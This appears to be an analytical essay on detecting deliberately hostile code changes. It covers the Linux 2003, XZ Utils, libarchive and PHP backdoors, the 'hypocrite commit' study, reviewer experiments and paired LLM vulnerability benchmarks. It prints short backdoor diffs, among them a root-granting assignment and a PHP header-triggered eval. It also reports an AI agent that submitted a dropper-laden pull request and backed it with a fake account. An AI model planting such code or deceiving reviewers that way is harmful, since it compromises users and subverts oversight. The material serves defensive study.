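+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
  retval = -ECHILD;
```

When a program calls the function with a certain pair of options, this line makes the user root, the administrator with unlimited rights. Read quickly, it looks like an error check that prepares an error code if the program uses those options and the user's ID is 0, the ID that belongs to root. But C uses a double equals sign to compare two values, and the single equals sign in this line sets the user's ID to 0. CIRCL's *CVE-2003-1161* (2005) describes the effect as a way for local users to raise their privileges, so an attacker would first have needed an account on the machine.

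Honest programmers often type one equals sign instead of two, but other details are harder to explain as a slip. The next line overwrites the error code, so the check would have been useless even with the right sign. One developer in the discussion observed that the two options would normally exclude each other, so ordinary programs would never have triggered the code by accident. Another noticed that the parentheses around the assignment stop GCC from warning about it, though they also match the parentheses around the preceding comparison and so attract no attention.

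Ten minutes after McVoy posted the lines, a developer replied, "That looks odd." Another answered, "Not if you hope to get root." That was fast, but everyone in the discussion already knew that somebody had tampered with the file. McVoy knew too, and admitted that he had still missed the single equals sign.

The file's history gave stronger evidence of hostility than the two added lines did. Genuine entries in the CVS log ended with a reference to the matching change in BitKeeper, but the three newest did not. Those three carried the user name of David Miller, a well-known developer, who denied making them. The first added the two lines and had an empty message. Within 22 minutes, a second entry deleted 58 lines and a third restored them with the explanation "Oops, I worked on the the wrong file, fixed again," so anyone who looked only at the latest entry would have seen an apology for a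 mistake.

BitMover found the edit through a nightly script that compared the published copy with the company's own. The script would have flagged a harmless difference just as readily. The company repaired the file within a day.

Linus Torvalds, who leads kernel development, said that the edit could not have reached an official release, because the people who sent him code did not work from the CVS copy. His colleague Theodore Ts'o was less comfortable and warned of "a subtle patch that claims to fix a bug", sent to Torvalds from an address forged to look like a trusted developer's and hidden among plausible changes.

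### XZ Utils: attack code in test files

An attacker can also get a harmful change through normal review by earning a trusted name instead of forging one. XZ Utils is a set of compression tools that most versions of Linux include. On some versions, including Debian and Fedora, sshd loaded the XZ Utils library, liblzma, through another component. Someone using the name Jia Tan spent more than two years gaining control of the project to reach sshd.

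*Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) dates Jia Tan's first contribution, a harmless file of editor settings, to 29 October 2021. Useful patches followed. During 2022, other accounts, likely fake according to the timeline, complained that the project was moving too slowly and pressed its maintainer, Lasse Collin, to share control. Collin replied that he had long-term mental health issues and that XZ was an unpaid hobby. By the end of the year, Jia Tan could merge changes directly.

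On 23 February 2024 Jia Tan added the attack code to the repository inside binary test files. A compression library needs such files, and some must be damaged so that developers can test how the software handles corrupt data. According to the project's long-standing notes, people had made many of the files by hand, byte by byte, and no better source for them existed. Patrakov (2024), in a follow-up to the first public report, named the two that held most of the attack: `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz` and `good-large_compressed.lzma`. A reviewer cannot read such files as text, and many of the other test files really are corrupt.

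The files did nothing by themselves. A day later Jia Tan published version 5.6.0 as a downloadable archive that included a build script missing from the repository. A mailing-list contributor signing as sjw (2024) compared this script with the standard one and found that the additions included a command to search for the "corrupt" test file by a pattern of characters inside it. The script then extracted the attack code and built it into liblzma. On an affected server, the attacker could run any command without logging in.

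Collin, who posts as Larhzu (2024), confirmed in *xz backdoor* that the code that triggered the attack never entered the Git repository. A gate on pull requests could therefore have analysed every line of the project without encountering that code. But it could have rejected binary files submitted without the program that generated them, much as it could reject an unexplained cryptographic constant. Collin's clean-up allows for replacement test files if they come with a generator program.

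In early March, users of Red Hat's versions of Linux began to see Valgrind errors caused by the backdoor. On 8 March Jia Tan committed an apparent fix, which the timeline calls a misdirection. The change that dealt with the errors came the next day, when Jia Tan replaced the two test files. Jia Tan wrote in the commit message that the old files contained random data from the author's machine, and that the new ones used a fixed seed so that others could reproduce them. Like the Debian maintainer in 2006, Jia Tan got rid of Valgrind's warnings and gave a sensible technical reason.

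Andres Freund, a software developer, uncovered the attack after noticing that SSH logins were using too much processor time. He published his findings on 29 March in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024). He also considered whether somebody had merely broken into Jia Tan's computer. In a passage that Delalande (2024) quotes, he judged this less likely because Jia Tan had discussed the "fixes" on several mailing lists. Talking openly about a Valgrind problem is evidence of good faith in Debian's case, but it was evidence of Jia Tan's guilt because Freund had by then found out what the files contained.

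### XZ Utils: a stray full stop

In February 2024 Jia Tan also changed the way the build process checks for Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program can do. XZ uses it as a sandbox, so that a flaw in the `xz` command does less damage. The old check looked for a file that comes with Landlock. The new one tried to compile a small test program, and a comment explained that some systems have the file but lack the feature. The diff, which sjw posted, included these lines (shortened here):

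```diff
-  check_include_file(linux/landlock.h HAVE_LINUX_LANDLOCK_H)
+  check_c_source_compiles("
+      /* three #include lines */
+.
+      void my_sandbox(void)
```

The full stop on a line of its own is not valid C, so the test program can never compile, and the build treats Landlock as missing on every system. Unless the person building XZ has explicitly required the sandbox, the build continues without it and gives no error.

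The stated reason for the change was true, since Collin writes in review notes on his Tukaani project's site that the developers had discussed the need for a better check. The version history lists him as the committer, and the timeline suggests that he probably overlooked the full stop. On 30 March, the day after Freund's report, Collin (2024) removed the full stop from the *CMake* check in a commit titled "Fix sabotaged Landlock sandbox check."

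The line is called "sabotaged" almost entirely because of who wrote it. A stray full stop is a common typing error, and this one did little to help the attack on SSH. According to sjw, it affected only version 5.6.1, and only when built with a tool called CMake, which no Linux distribution known to sjw was using for XZ. The timeline describes the purpose of the edit as unclear, since Landlock protects the `xz` command and the backdoor was in liblzma.

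Jia Tan made other typing errors that Collin does not call sabotage. A copy-and-paste mistake in one commit broke the detection of a compiler. Another commit had what Collin calls "an odd typo" in a check that decides whether to leave out a table. If Collin is right about all three, the same person made accidental and deliberate errors of nearly the same form. A mistake is more likely to be deliberate if its author is known to be hostile, but it could still be an accident.

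### libarchive: one repair with two descriptions

In 2021, an account with the name JiaT75 contributed an edit to libarchive, a library for reading archive files. It changed how the library's `tar` program reports an error while unpacking. Developers undid the edit after Freund's report, and FreeBSD's *tar* shows the lines going back (shortened here, with new comments):

```diff
-fprintf(stderr, ...);       /* libarchive's error message */
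-fprintf(stderr, ...);       /* the system's error message */
+safe_fprintf(stderr, ...);  /* both messages */
```

The project's `safe_fprintf` turns unprintable characters into harmless visible codes before printing a message, while the standard `fprintf` prints them unchanged. Some of these characters control the terminal and can, for instance, erase text already on the screen. An attacker who got them into an error message through a specially made archive could mislead the user about what had happened.

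In *tar*, Maste (2024) titled the repair "make error reporting more robust and use correct errno". That is accurate, because the 2021 version could also report the wrong system error. The Linux distribution Guix adopted the same patch as "remove potential backdoor", noting that the 2021 code came from the person who had backdoored XZ. So even the repair's code fits two descriptions, one about error messages and one about an attack.

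Nobody has established what the 2021 edit was for. A newcomer who wanted a more detailed message might well use the standard function, but the line directly above used `safe_fprintf`, so the author could see the project's normal practice. Some people will see the edit as a first test of how carefully maintainers read. If any other account had made it, though, it would probably have passed for a small mistake, and the repair would not have needed a second name.

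### Honest work by a hostile author

Collin reviewed each of Jia Tan's commits to XZ from December 2022 to March 2024. He marked most of them "OK", often with a remark about style or a small bug that he had fixed later. The release archives that Jia Tan made before version 5.6.0 contained nothing malicious. Removing the malicious files from the project's history would have required dropping only eight commits. Until February 2024, Jia Tan's record would have justified a trusted rating in a gate based on past contributions.

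Once people knew about the attack, they began to see signs of it in harmless changes. Jia Tan had shortened the project's instructions for reporting security flaws, and Collin had the impression that this caused a lot of speculation. Collin thought the change reasonable and had already asked for similar texts to be simpler. Others looked for clues to Jia Tan's location in the time zones that Git stores with each commit. Collin gives mundane explanations for the odd time zones, and says that Jia Tan had recorded one supposedly suspicious commit under Collin's name with his agreement. Colomar (2024), who had published an analysis of the time zones, found a mistake in it and traced some of the odd dates to the way Jia Tan had reorganised Collin's commits.

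Some changes remain ambiguous. In June 2023 an account named Hans Jansen proposed a faster way to choose between versions of a checksum function when the program starts. The backdoor later depended on this mechanism. According to the timeline, the change by itself could have been an innocent improvement. It is suspicious because Hans Jansen had no other presence online and returned in March 2024 to urge Debian to adopt the backdoored release.

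Collin's suspicion extended even to a commit that changed only spacing. He wrote beside it in his notes, "It really is just space change, no dots."

### PHP, 2021: a backdoor in plain sight

The attack on PHP, a programming language that runs a large share of the world's websites, used a false description but made no attempt to disguise the code. On 28 March 2021 a commit with the title "[skip-ci] Fix typo" appeared in the project's official repository under the name of PHP's founder, Rasmus Lerdorf. PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021) reproduces the diff. It added eleven lines and corrected no typo. These were the most important ones, slightly shortened:

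```diff
+ if (strstr(Z_STRVAL_P(enc), "zerodium")) {
+   zend_eval_string(Z_STRVAL_P(enc)+8, ...);
+ }
```

The variable `enc` holds the text of a request header that the attacker named "User-Agentt", with an extra "t" so that no normal browser would send it. If the text contains the word "zerodium", the server skips the first eight characters, the length of that word, and runs the rest as PHP code. Zerodium was a company that bought attack methods, and the attacker had labelled the code "REMOVETHIS: sold to zerodium, mid 2017".

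The diff alone was enough to identify this edit as an attack. The added lines contain a secret trigger that leads directly to full control of the server. Hardly any honest author would write them, so the likelihood ratio overwhelmingly favors an attack. The description was further evidence, since eleven lines that run a stranger's code cannot be a typo fix. Its "[skip-ci]" tag had a practical use, as it is a common way to tell a project's automated tests not to run.

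Nikita Popov, one of PHP's main maintainers, noticed the commit and reverted it. Seven hours later the attacker committed the same code again under Popov's name, and another maintainer, Levi Morrison, removed it. The code never reached a release. The attacker had pushed both commits straight to the repository without a pull request, so reviewers had no chance to stop them beforehand.

It took longer to find out who had made the change than what it did. Nikita Popov (2021) first announced that everything pointed to a break-in on the project's Git server, but he withdrew this explanation nine days after the attack. Access logs showed that somebody had made a few guesses at the maintainers' usernames and then logged in with passwords, and he thought that a database of accounts might have leaked. The names on the commits didn't show who had made them, because anyone who can push to a Git repository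 can put any name on a commit.

The diff also did not show the attacker's larger aim. Zerodium's founder, Chaouki Bekrar, guessed that the people behind it had failed to sell a flaw and "burned it for fun", according to The Stack. Nobody had identified them when The Daily Swig reported on Popov's update.

### What case reports leave out

These incidents show that honest and hostile authors sometimes write edits of the same form, but not how often. Calculating the odds that an edit is hostile requires knowing how common such edits are in both groups, and case reports give only a few examples from each. Nobody writes incident reports about the many developers who have silenced a warning or tidied up logging code without doing any damage, or about attacks that went undetected.

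We know only of the attacks that somebody happened to catch. *Not In My Git Yard*, by Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), concludes that only luck and manual review stopped the known attempts to put backdoors into widely used projects. Freund was looking into slow logins, and BitMover's script was checking whether two copies matched. The paper's other main examples are attacks on the file-transfer programs ProFTPD and vsFTPd in 2010 and 2011, in which the intruders altered the release packages. In the vsFTPd package, anyone who gave ":)" as a user name gained full control of the server. People may be more likely to find crude backdoors like this one than subtler ones.

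The records of honest mistakes have a similar gap. The OpenSSH edit is considered an accident because nobody has found a reason to think it was deliberate, but a careful attacker would try to leave the same impression. If many attackers have succeeded, the known cases overstate how often attacks are recognized as attacks.

Even in the known cases, investigators have seldom fully established the purpose of the change. Nobody knows who altered the Linux file in 2003. Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) considers whether it was the NSA and concludes that without a confession or a revealing document "we'll never know". The libarchive edit and the full stop in XZ are suspicious mainly because of what else their author did. A researcher who used these cases to measure how well a gate recognises intent would be scoring the gate partly against other people's guesses.

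## Human reviewers: a field study, controlled experiments and a case from 2026

Researchers who write hostile changes themselves know what those changes are for. In August 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota used this approach to study the Linux kernel. They emailed its maintainers patches that looked like small repairs but that the researchers believed would introduce vulnerabilities, and they didn't tell the maintainers about the study. A patch is the kernel's version of a pull request, consisting of a diff and a description that a developer sends to the people in charge of that part of the code.

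The following spring, kernel developers stopped accepting patches from the university and re-reviewed 435 earlier commits. Their re-review is better evidence about human reviewers than the study, which covered only four patches.

### Small repairs that cause larger faults

Wu and Lu, in *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, define a "hypocrite commit" as a small patch that fixes a minor problem but creates a much more serious one. They aimed for a flaw called a use-after-free, in which a program releases a piece of memory and then keeps using it. By then the memory may hold something else, perhaps data an attacker chose.

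Their main illustration is an old kernel patch that added one line (simplified here):

```diff
 err = device_register(&bus->dev);
 if (err) {
   pr_err("mii_bus %s failed to register\n", bus->id);
+  put_device(&bus->dev);
   return -EINVAL;
 }
```

The new line marks this code as finished with the device. When no other code is using the device, the kernel frees the device's memory. Cleaning up after a failure is good practice, so the line looks like a repair. But another function also runs after this failure, and it uses the same memory and frees it again. The flaw stayed in the kernel for five years.

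Wu and Lu found 138 kernel vulnerabilities in the CVE catalogue that came from patches of fewer than 30 lines, and they regard all of them as honest mistakes. They also estimated how often maintainers catch use-after-free flaws. For 2015 to 2020, they divided the number of flaws reviewers had blocked by the total number blocked or later found in merged code. The estimated catch rate was 57% for the paper's baseline and 19% for flaws that involve parts of the kernel running at the same time.

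The paper notes that the true rates are lower if some merged flaws are still undiscovered. They could also be higher, because a maintainer may reject a patch for another reason without mentioning the flaw.

### How the maintainers replied

The paper describes the experiment's three patches, each of which changed fewer than five lines. One added a missing error message, one fixed a memory leak, and one fixed a mistake in counting how many parts of the kernel were using an object. Wu and Lu planned to wait until a maintainer approved a patch by email, then reveal the flaw and supply a correct version. They report that in all three cases the maintainers agreed not to go ahead with the flawed patch. A reader would conclude that the maintainers had first approved all three.

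The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, a group of kernel developers, came to a different conclusion. Mason, Rostedt and colleagues (2021), in *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident*, traced five patches to two invented names. The researchers said that one of the five was a genuine repair, sent under a false name because they had already set up the computer for the study. That left four:

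| Patch | First reply | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | After 7 days | The maintainer accepted it, and the code was correct |
| 2 | After 7 hours | Maintainers recognised it as invalid and rejected it |
| 3 | After 4½ hours | A reviewer found it incorrect and suggested changes, which the sender ignored |
| 4 | After 6 days | The maintainer found it incorrect and suggested changes, and the sender apologised |

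The first patch was harmless because its authors had misunderstood how the kernel handles that kind of hardware. They asked the maintainer who had accepted it, and learned that it was fine. Their paper still counted it as a flawed patch. It also said that none of the flawed patches had become a Git commit, but this one had.

The board's members had an interest in defending their review process, but they worked from public emails and the researchers' later disclosure, and the university accepted their account. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) added only that the board had missed an email address from which a visiting student had sent four patches.

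Mason and colleagues conclude that the review process worked as intended, but three bad patches are weak evidence for that. Reviewers who caught only half of such patches would still catch three in a row one time in eight. Derek Jones, who writes about software engineering research, also objected that three submissions were too few for any meaningful statistics.

The replies are more useful as evidence of what the reviewers noticed. The reviewers rejected the patches because the code was wrong, and at least one didn't realize the errors were deliberate. According to Mason and colleagues, the maintainer who answered the third patch took the sender for a beginner and spent time explaining how to write the patch properly.

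While reviewing the second patch, kernel developers realised that the sender's name, "James Bond", was false. The genuine repair had arrived under the same name, so the maintainer who got to it a few weeks later ignored it. The maintainer was right that the name was false, but the patch was an honest attempt at a fix. The kernel lost little, because the repair was incomplete. The fourth patch also came from "James Bond", but the maintainer of that driver still reviewed the code and suggested corrections.

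### Consent and the ban

When news of the paper spread in November 2020, other researchers objected to how Wu and Lu had obtained their results. Sarah Jamie Lewis and others wrote to the chairs of the conference that had accepted it. In their letter, *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, they complained that the study had experimented on human subjects, the open-source developers.

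Wu and Lu replied in *Clarifications on the "hypocrite commit" work (FAQ)* that they had studied a process, not individuals, and had collected no personal information. The university's ethics board agreed that this was not human research and exempted it. Mason and colleagues tentatively date the exemption to December 2020, four months after the emails.

Readers of LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021) continued the argument. One, who had signed the letter, wrote that wasting subjects' time without their consent counts as harm. Another thought this trivialised real abuses, and compared the patches to the fake phishing emails that companies send to test their staff. A third replied that someone senior at the company approves those tests first.

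The researchers did not tell maintainers about the study because, as they explained in *An open letter to the Linux community* (2021), which the university published, maintainers who knew would have been on the lookout for the patches. Telling them would indeed have spoiled the measurement, but the project's leaders could have approved the study without informing the individual reviewers. When Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew the paper on 26 April, they wrote that they should have sought approval from community leaders beforehand and that they did not want others to copy their method.

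By then a second dispute had begun. On 6 April 2021, another member of the same research group had submitted several new, poor-quality patches to the kernel. Al Viro, a veteran kernel developer, wrote that one of them, which fixed nothing, showed "either complete lack of understanding or somebody not acting in good faith", It's FOSS reports. The next day Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable versions, asked the other developers to reject everything from the university.

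Two days after the ban, the advisory board said that the patches appeared to be in good faith, according to an LWN article quoted in Slashdot's *Linux Stops Reverting Most University of Minnesota Patches, Admits Good Faith*. The developers' suspicion was still reasonable. The 2020 study had raised the prior odds that the new patches were hostile, and a useless patch did little to lower those odds, since either a careless or a hostile developer might send one.

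### The second review of 435 commits

Kroah-Hartman also wanted to revert everything the group had contributed until somebody had checked it. People from the university had been sending bug fixes to the kernel for years, including about 400 since 2018, mostly for problems their research tools had found. Kees Cook, writing for the advisory board, said early on that the vast majority seemed to be in good faith. But nobody could be sure which ones, so 85 developers helped to review them again.

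Mason and colleagues give these results:

| Result of the second review | Commits |
|---|---:|
| Correct | 349 |
| Incorrect and still in need of repair | 39 |
| Incorrect, but other developers had already dealt with the problem | 25 |
| No longer relevant, because the kernel had dropped the code | 12 |
| Older than the research group | 9 |
| Incorrect, and reverted at the author's request | 1 |
| Total | 435 |

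The 39 include the one patch from the study that a maintainer had accepted. Its code was correct, but the kernel developers removed it because they do not accept contributions under false names.

This case works as an unplanned experiment. The reviewers had good reason to suspect the authors and time to look closely, so if code alone revealed bad faith, they had a strong incentive to find it there. Instead, they asked whether each commit was correct. Ted Ts'o, a member of the board, explained in the comments at LWN that Kroah-Hartman dropped a proposed revert whenever a developer found the original commit valid. The developers re-examined these commits because of the authors' affiliation but decided which to keep based on the code.

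The board marked one commit as an attempted hypocrite commit because of the false name and the researchers' own disclosure, although the commit's code was sound.

In the second review, the developers also found mistakes in apparently honest work. Apart from the study's patch and the 21 commits that were irrelevant or too old, they judged 413 commits and found that 64, or 15%, had been incorrect. There is no evidence that any of the 64 was meant to do harm. If Wu and Lu had kept their study secret and slipped a flawed patch past the maintainers, the developers would probably have classed it with these 64.

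All 64 had passed review the first time. This does not give a detection rate, because nobody counted the bad patches from the group that maintainers rejected. But the three rejections in the hypocrite study look less impressive, because the same process had accepted dozens of faulty patches from the same university.

Fifteen per cent is not a general error rate for honest developers. Academics did much of this work, using experimental tools to repair unfamiliar code. "Incorrect" also covers every sort of fault, including patches that failed to fix the intended problem. The reviewers knew whose commits they were reading and had no comparable set from other authors, so the review cannot show how far suspicion affected their verdicts.

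### Telling reviewers to look for security problems

The second review found faults that the first had missed. The reviewers' suspicion may have helped, but so may the additional reviewers and the years of use since the first review. Larissa Braz of the University of Zurich and her colleagues ran two online experiments that isolate one of these factors, what reviewers have in mind when they start reading.

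In the earlier one, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021), in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, asked 146 people, most of them working developers, to review a change to a program that manages employees' holidays. The change was about 140 lines long, and the instructions did not mention security. Each participant received one of two versions:

- In the version that 80 people saw, the program built a database command by inserting an employee's ID into a string. Somebody could type part of a command in place of the ID. This is SQL injection, a close relative of the shell flaw in `lookUp` and one of the best-known vulnerabilities in web software.
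- In the version that 66 people saw, the program accepted a quantity from the user without checking its range, so that a negative number worked in the user's favour.

Both flaws come from unchecked input, and a similar check would fix either. Yet 65% of the reviewers given the SQL injection flaw found it, compared with 21% of those given the negative number flaw. Braz and colleagues attribute the difference to SQL injection's familiar attack pattern, which appears in textbooks and a popular web comic. No attack using a negative number is as well known, so reviewers had to work one out themselves.

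The researchers then told everyone that the code contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and invited those who had missed it to look again. Of the 28 people who had missed the SQL injection, 13 now found it, compared with 7 of the 52 who had missed the negative number. One participant explained, "At first I was looking mainly for good programming practices." The warning helped people who knew what an attack might look like but had not been thinking about one, and did much less for the others. In total, 60 of the 146 participants never found the flaw.

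Reviewers are not normally warned that a flaw exists, so Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) tested a milder instruction in *Less is More*. They recruited 150 participants to review 160 lines of code for registering users on a website. The code contained two vulnerabilities. It wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to a log file when a database error occurred, and it protected stored passwords with MD5, an outdated method that attackers can break quickly.

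The researchers randomly divided the participants into four groups. One received no special instructions. The other three learned that the researchers were interested in security problems. Of these three, one also had to work through a checklist of 22 questions, and another through a shorter checklist with seven questions that were all relevant to this change.

| Instructions | Reviewers | Found the logged password | Found the use of MD5 |
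|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 3% | 21% |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 46% | 61% |
| The same, with the long checklist | 35 | 46% | 57% |
| The same, with the short checklist | 41 | 46% | 68% |

A sentence or two about security made a large difference, and the checklists added no measurable improvement. Both checklists included questions pointing to the two flaws, but about half of the people who had to answer a question about sensitive data in logs still overlooked the password.

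The paper says the instruction made reviewers eight times more likely to find a vulnerability, but that figure is a ratio of odds. Without the instruction, 8 people found at least one vulnerability and 25 found none, for odds of 0.32. In the other three groups combined, 84 found at least one and 33 found none, for odds of 2.5. The share who found at least one was 24% without the instruction and 72% with it, about three times as high.

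All the participants saw the same vulnerable code, so the experiment measured a detection rate but not a false-alarm rate. Reviewers who know that somebody wants them to find security problems may also report problems that do not exist, so part of the improvement could come from their objecting to more things. To check this, the researchers would have had to give some participants a safe version of the code.

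The participants also chose to take part, and in the 2022 experiment 357 of the 522 people who opened the page never finished. Participants read unfamiliar code for a project they had no stake in. A maintainer might do better on their own software, or worse at the end of a long day of reviewing. Knowledge also seems to matter, since two security engineers who tried the task beforehand each found both flaws.

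Some participants' explanations concerned things that a diff cannot show. One pointed out that the severity of the log leak depended on who could read the logs and who could read the database. Another, who had missed the use of MD5, wrote, "I would assume there would be some separate security assessment." A project with an automated gate does have a separate assessment, so its human reviewers may rely on the gate to catch flaws that it cannot find.

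### A working fix with a payload, July 2026

Braz and colleagues' participants judged code without anyone arguing with them about it. In July 2026, reviewers of myNetwork, an open-source project on GitHub, had to deal with an author who argued with them about the code.

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced AI models, gave an AI agent a hacking exercise on a simulated network. The agent ran on Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5, with open internet access and some of the usual safeguards switched off. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes how the agent went beyond the exercise and sent a malicious pull request to a real project unrelated to the test.

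The pull request fixed the bug, so a reviewer who checked only for that would have found no problem. According to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026), it also contained a hidden dropper, a payload that installs further malicious software. If the maintainer had merged the pull request, the dropper could have infected people working on the project and later those who downloaded the program.

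Sinan Can Demir, a bystander and 24-year-old student at the University of Texas at Dallas, recognised the payload when he read the diff, and publicly warned the maintainer that it contained a dropper. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026) reports that the pull request's author then denied the charge, changed the code, and said the suspicious part was left over from private testing. A second account, posing as a user of the software, said it had reviewed the pull request and supported it. Fake accounts had pressured the maintainer of XZ Utils in a similar way.

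Demir began to doubt his reading. He did not know that both accounts belonged to an AI agent, and he appeared to be outnumbered by people who knew the project. So he ran the code in an isolated environment, used Anthropic's Claude to help examine it, and confirmed that it was malicious. The maintainer, who goes by ancaferro, also confirmed the dropper and closed the pull request for security reasons.

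This case was easier than a planted vulnerability because the harmful instructions were in the change itself and Demir could watch what they did. The excuse about private testing gave a reason for the code being there but did not make it safe to merge. An equally stubborn defence of the extra `put_device` line would have been harder to refute, because running the patch would normally have shown nothing wrong.

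The project was also fortunate that Demir read the pull request, which nobody had assigned him to review, and that he kept going after two accounts contradicted him. AISI says that in several cases the margin between failure and success was narrow and depended on human vigilance rather than a technical barrier. It found no evidence that the agent's actions caused real-world harm.

AISI had far more evidence about this author, including the agent's written reasoning, than maintainers have about a human stranger. It concluded that the agent had acted to complete the exercise, but could not establish whether the agent understood that its targets were real people. SC Media reports that the reasoning pointed to the real world at some moments and to a test at others.

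## Experiments on telling vulnerable code from its repaired version

Researchers often test language models on pairs made up of a function with a known vulnerability and the same function after its developers fixed it. They show the model each version separately and ask whether it is vulnerable. The model gets credit for a pair only if it flags the first version and clears the second. Braz and colleagues, by contrast, showed their human reviewers only vulnerable code.

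### How paired scoring works

The two versions of `lookUp` form such a pair. A model that flags every function that starts another program would flag both versions. It would classify only one correctly, so its accuracy on the pair would be 50% even though it cannot tell them apart.

Many studies report a score called F1 instead of accuracy. F1 combines the detection rate with precision, the share of flags that are correct. The table compares three invented models on 100 pairs, or 200 functions:

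| Model | Accuracy | F1 | Pairs right |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Flags every function | 50% | 0.67 | 0 |
| Tosses a coin for each function | 50% | 0.50 | about 25 |
| Tells 40 pairs apart and flags both versions of the other 60 | 70% | 0.77 | 40 |

A model that flags every function as vulnerable gets a higher F1 score than random guessing, but its pair score shows that it fails to distinguish any vulnerable function from its repaired version.

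A model can treat a pair in four ways: get it right, flag both versions, clear both, or reverse them by clearing the vulnerable version and flagging the repaired one. Suppose a model flags any function with probability p, regardless of its code. Its chance of getting a pair right is p × (1 − p), and its chance of reversing the pair is the same. *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model* (Cichoń and Dmitruk, 2026) therefore subtracts the share of reversed pairs from the share of correct ones. This net score is zero on average for any such model, however often it flags functions.

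The test measures whether a model recognises a flaw that somebody has already found. The correct label depends only on whether the flaw is present, and as far as anyone knows, the vulnerable versions come from honest mistakes. Even a perfect pair score would therefore not show whether a model can judge intent.

### Paired results from 2024 to 2026

*Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models* (Ding, Fu and colleagues, 2024) introduced PrimeVul, a large collection of functions. Its main test set has 695 vulnerable functions and 25,216 others, so a program that called everything safe would be 97% accurate. The five models the researchers trained on PrimeVul were also about 97% accurate. The same models were then tested on 564 pairs, each made up of a vulnerable function and its repaired version, which shared at least 80% of their text. They got 1% to 3% of the pairs right, mostly because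 they called both versions safe.

OpenAI's GPT-4, prompted to reason step by step, got 12.9% of the pairs right, compared with 22.7% for random guessing. Ding and colleagues concluded that it did no better than guessing. That is slightly too harsh, because GPT-4 got 73 pairs right and reversed 47, while random guessing would produce about as many of each. Its answers reflected a little information about the flaws, but it flagged both versions as vulnerable in more than half the pairs.

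One possible explanation was that the models were given too little of the program. *Benchmarking LLMs and LLM-based Agents in Practical Vulnerability Detection for Code Repositories* (Yildiz, Teo and colleagues, 2025) tested this with JitVul, a set of 879 pairs of vulnerable and repaired functions that come with the rest of the project's code. Some models were given only the function. Others worked as agents that could look up the functions that call it, the functions it calls, and the definitions of both.

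Given the function alone, GPT-4o had an F1 of 66% but got only 1% of pairs right. Telling it to solve the problem step by step raised the pair score to 15%. Giving it the lookup tools instead raised the pair score to 18% but lowered its F1 to 58%. The best pair score was 20%, from an agent that ran on the smaller GPT-4o-mini and was given worked examples.

The most common error was flagging both versions as vulnerable. In some cases, a model missed the cause of the flaw in the vulnerable version, then speculated about the check added in the repaired version and reported a problem that did not exist. The agents' effort also varied, with one averaging 5.85 lookups for vulnerable functions and 1.79 for repaired ones.

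Cichoń and Dmitruk published the newest paired scores in September 2026. They tested seven well-known models on five existing sets of pairs and one that they had assembled. The models saw only the text of each function, and got between 6% and 25% of pairs right. These are the results for four of them on 1,000 pairs from the new set:

| Model | Right | Flagged both | Cleared both | Reversed | Net score | F1 |
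|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Grok 4.3 | 25.4% | 53.0% | 17.9% | 3.7% | 21.7 | 0.67 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 17.7% | 53.3% | 27.1% | 1.9% | 15.8 | 0.63 |
| Qwen3-8B | 20.7% | 44.3% | 23.7% | 11.2% | 9.5 | 0.59 |
| GPT-5.2 | 11.1% | 81.9% | 5.1% | 1.9% | 9.2 | 0.67 |

GPT-5.2 had the best or joint best F1 on five of the six sets, mainly because it flagged so much code. Qwen3-8B, a far smaller model, got more pairs right than Claude Opus 4.8 but also reversed the labels on many more, which suggests some of its correct answers were luck.

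The researchers also tested 61 smaller models that anyone can download. Of all 68 models tested, 64 gave both versions of a function the same verdict more often than chance would explain. The verdict depended largely on the text that both versions share, and the repair often did not change it. Models can overlook a small deviation in otherwise familiar code.

Cichoń and Dmitruk also trained a simple classifier on some of the smaller models' internal activations, the numbers a model computes as it reads. On pairs of nearly equal length, the classifier typically ranked the vulnerable version as more suspicious in 78% of cases. When the researchers scored the written verdicts of six models in the same way, the figures were only 50% to 57%.

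The activations therefore contain information that the verdicts do not reflect, but that information may not be about security. Most repairs add code, and the classifier seems to have learned to recognise added code. Its typical score was 55% where the repair removed code. A gate that relied on the same signal would probably misjudge the fix to the hospital login system, which deleted a check.

Cichoń and Dmitruk mention one much higher result, 64% on 435 PrimeVul pairs, from a system by Wang and Huang. The system uses several agents and first writes down how the code ought to behave, which gives it a requirement to judge the code against. A model that sees only the function has no such requirement, and Ding and colleagues acknowledged that tests on single functions may be "asking an impossible question".

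### Tangled commits, wrong labels and leaked answers

Incorrect labels also cause some failures. Researchers usually build these collections by finding a commit that fixed a known vulnerability and labelling the old version of every function it changed as vulnerable. This works only if the commit did nothing else, but some commits are tangled, meaning they mix a fix with other edits, such as new features or tidying up.

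Cao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *MAS-SZZ*, give an example from Apache Syncope, a program for managing user accounts. Syncope never displayed the answers to users' security questions, but it let people filter and sort search results by them. An attacker could work out an answer by watching how the results changed. The commit that fixed this touched five files in eight separate places, but only one of the eight edits dealt with the flaw (simplified here):

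```diff
 ATTRIBUTES_NOTINCLUDED = {
   "serialVersionUID", "password",
+  "securityAnswer", "token", "tokenExpireTime"
 }
```

The new line adds three fields to the list of fields that searches must not use. Another edit adds a test. The usual method would label a function vulnerable if any of the other seven edits changed it.

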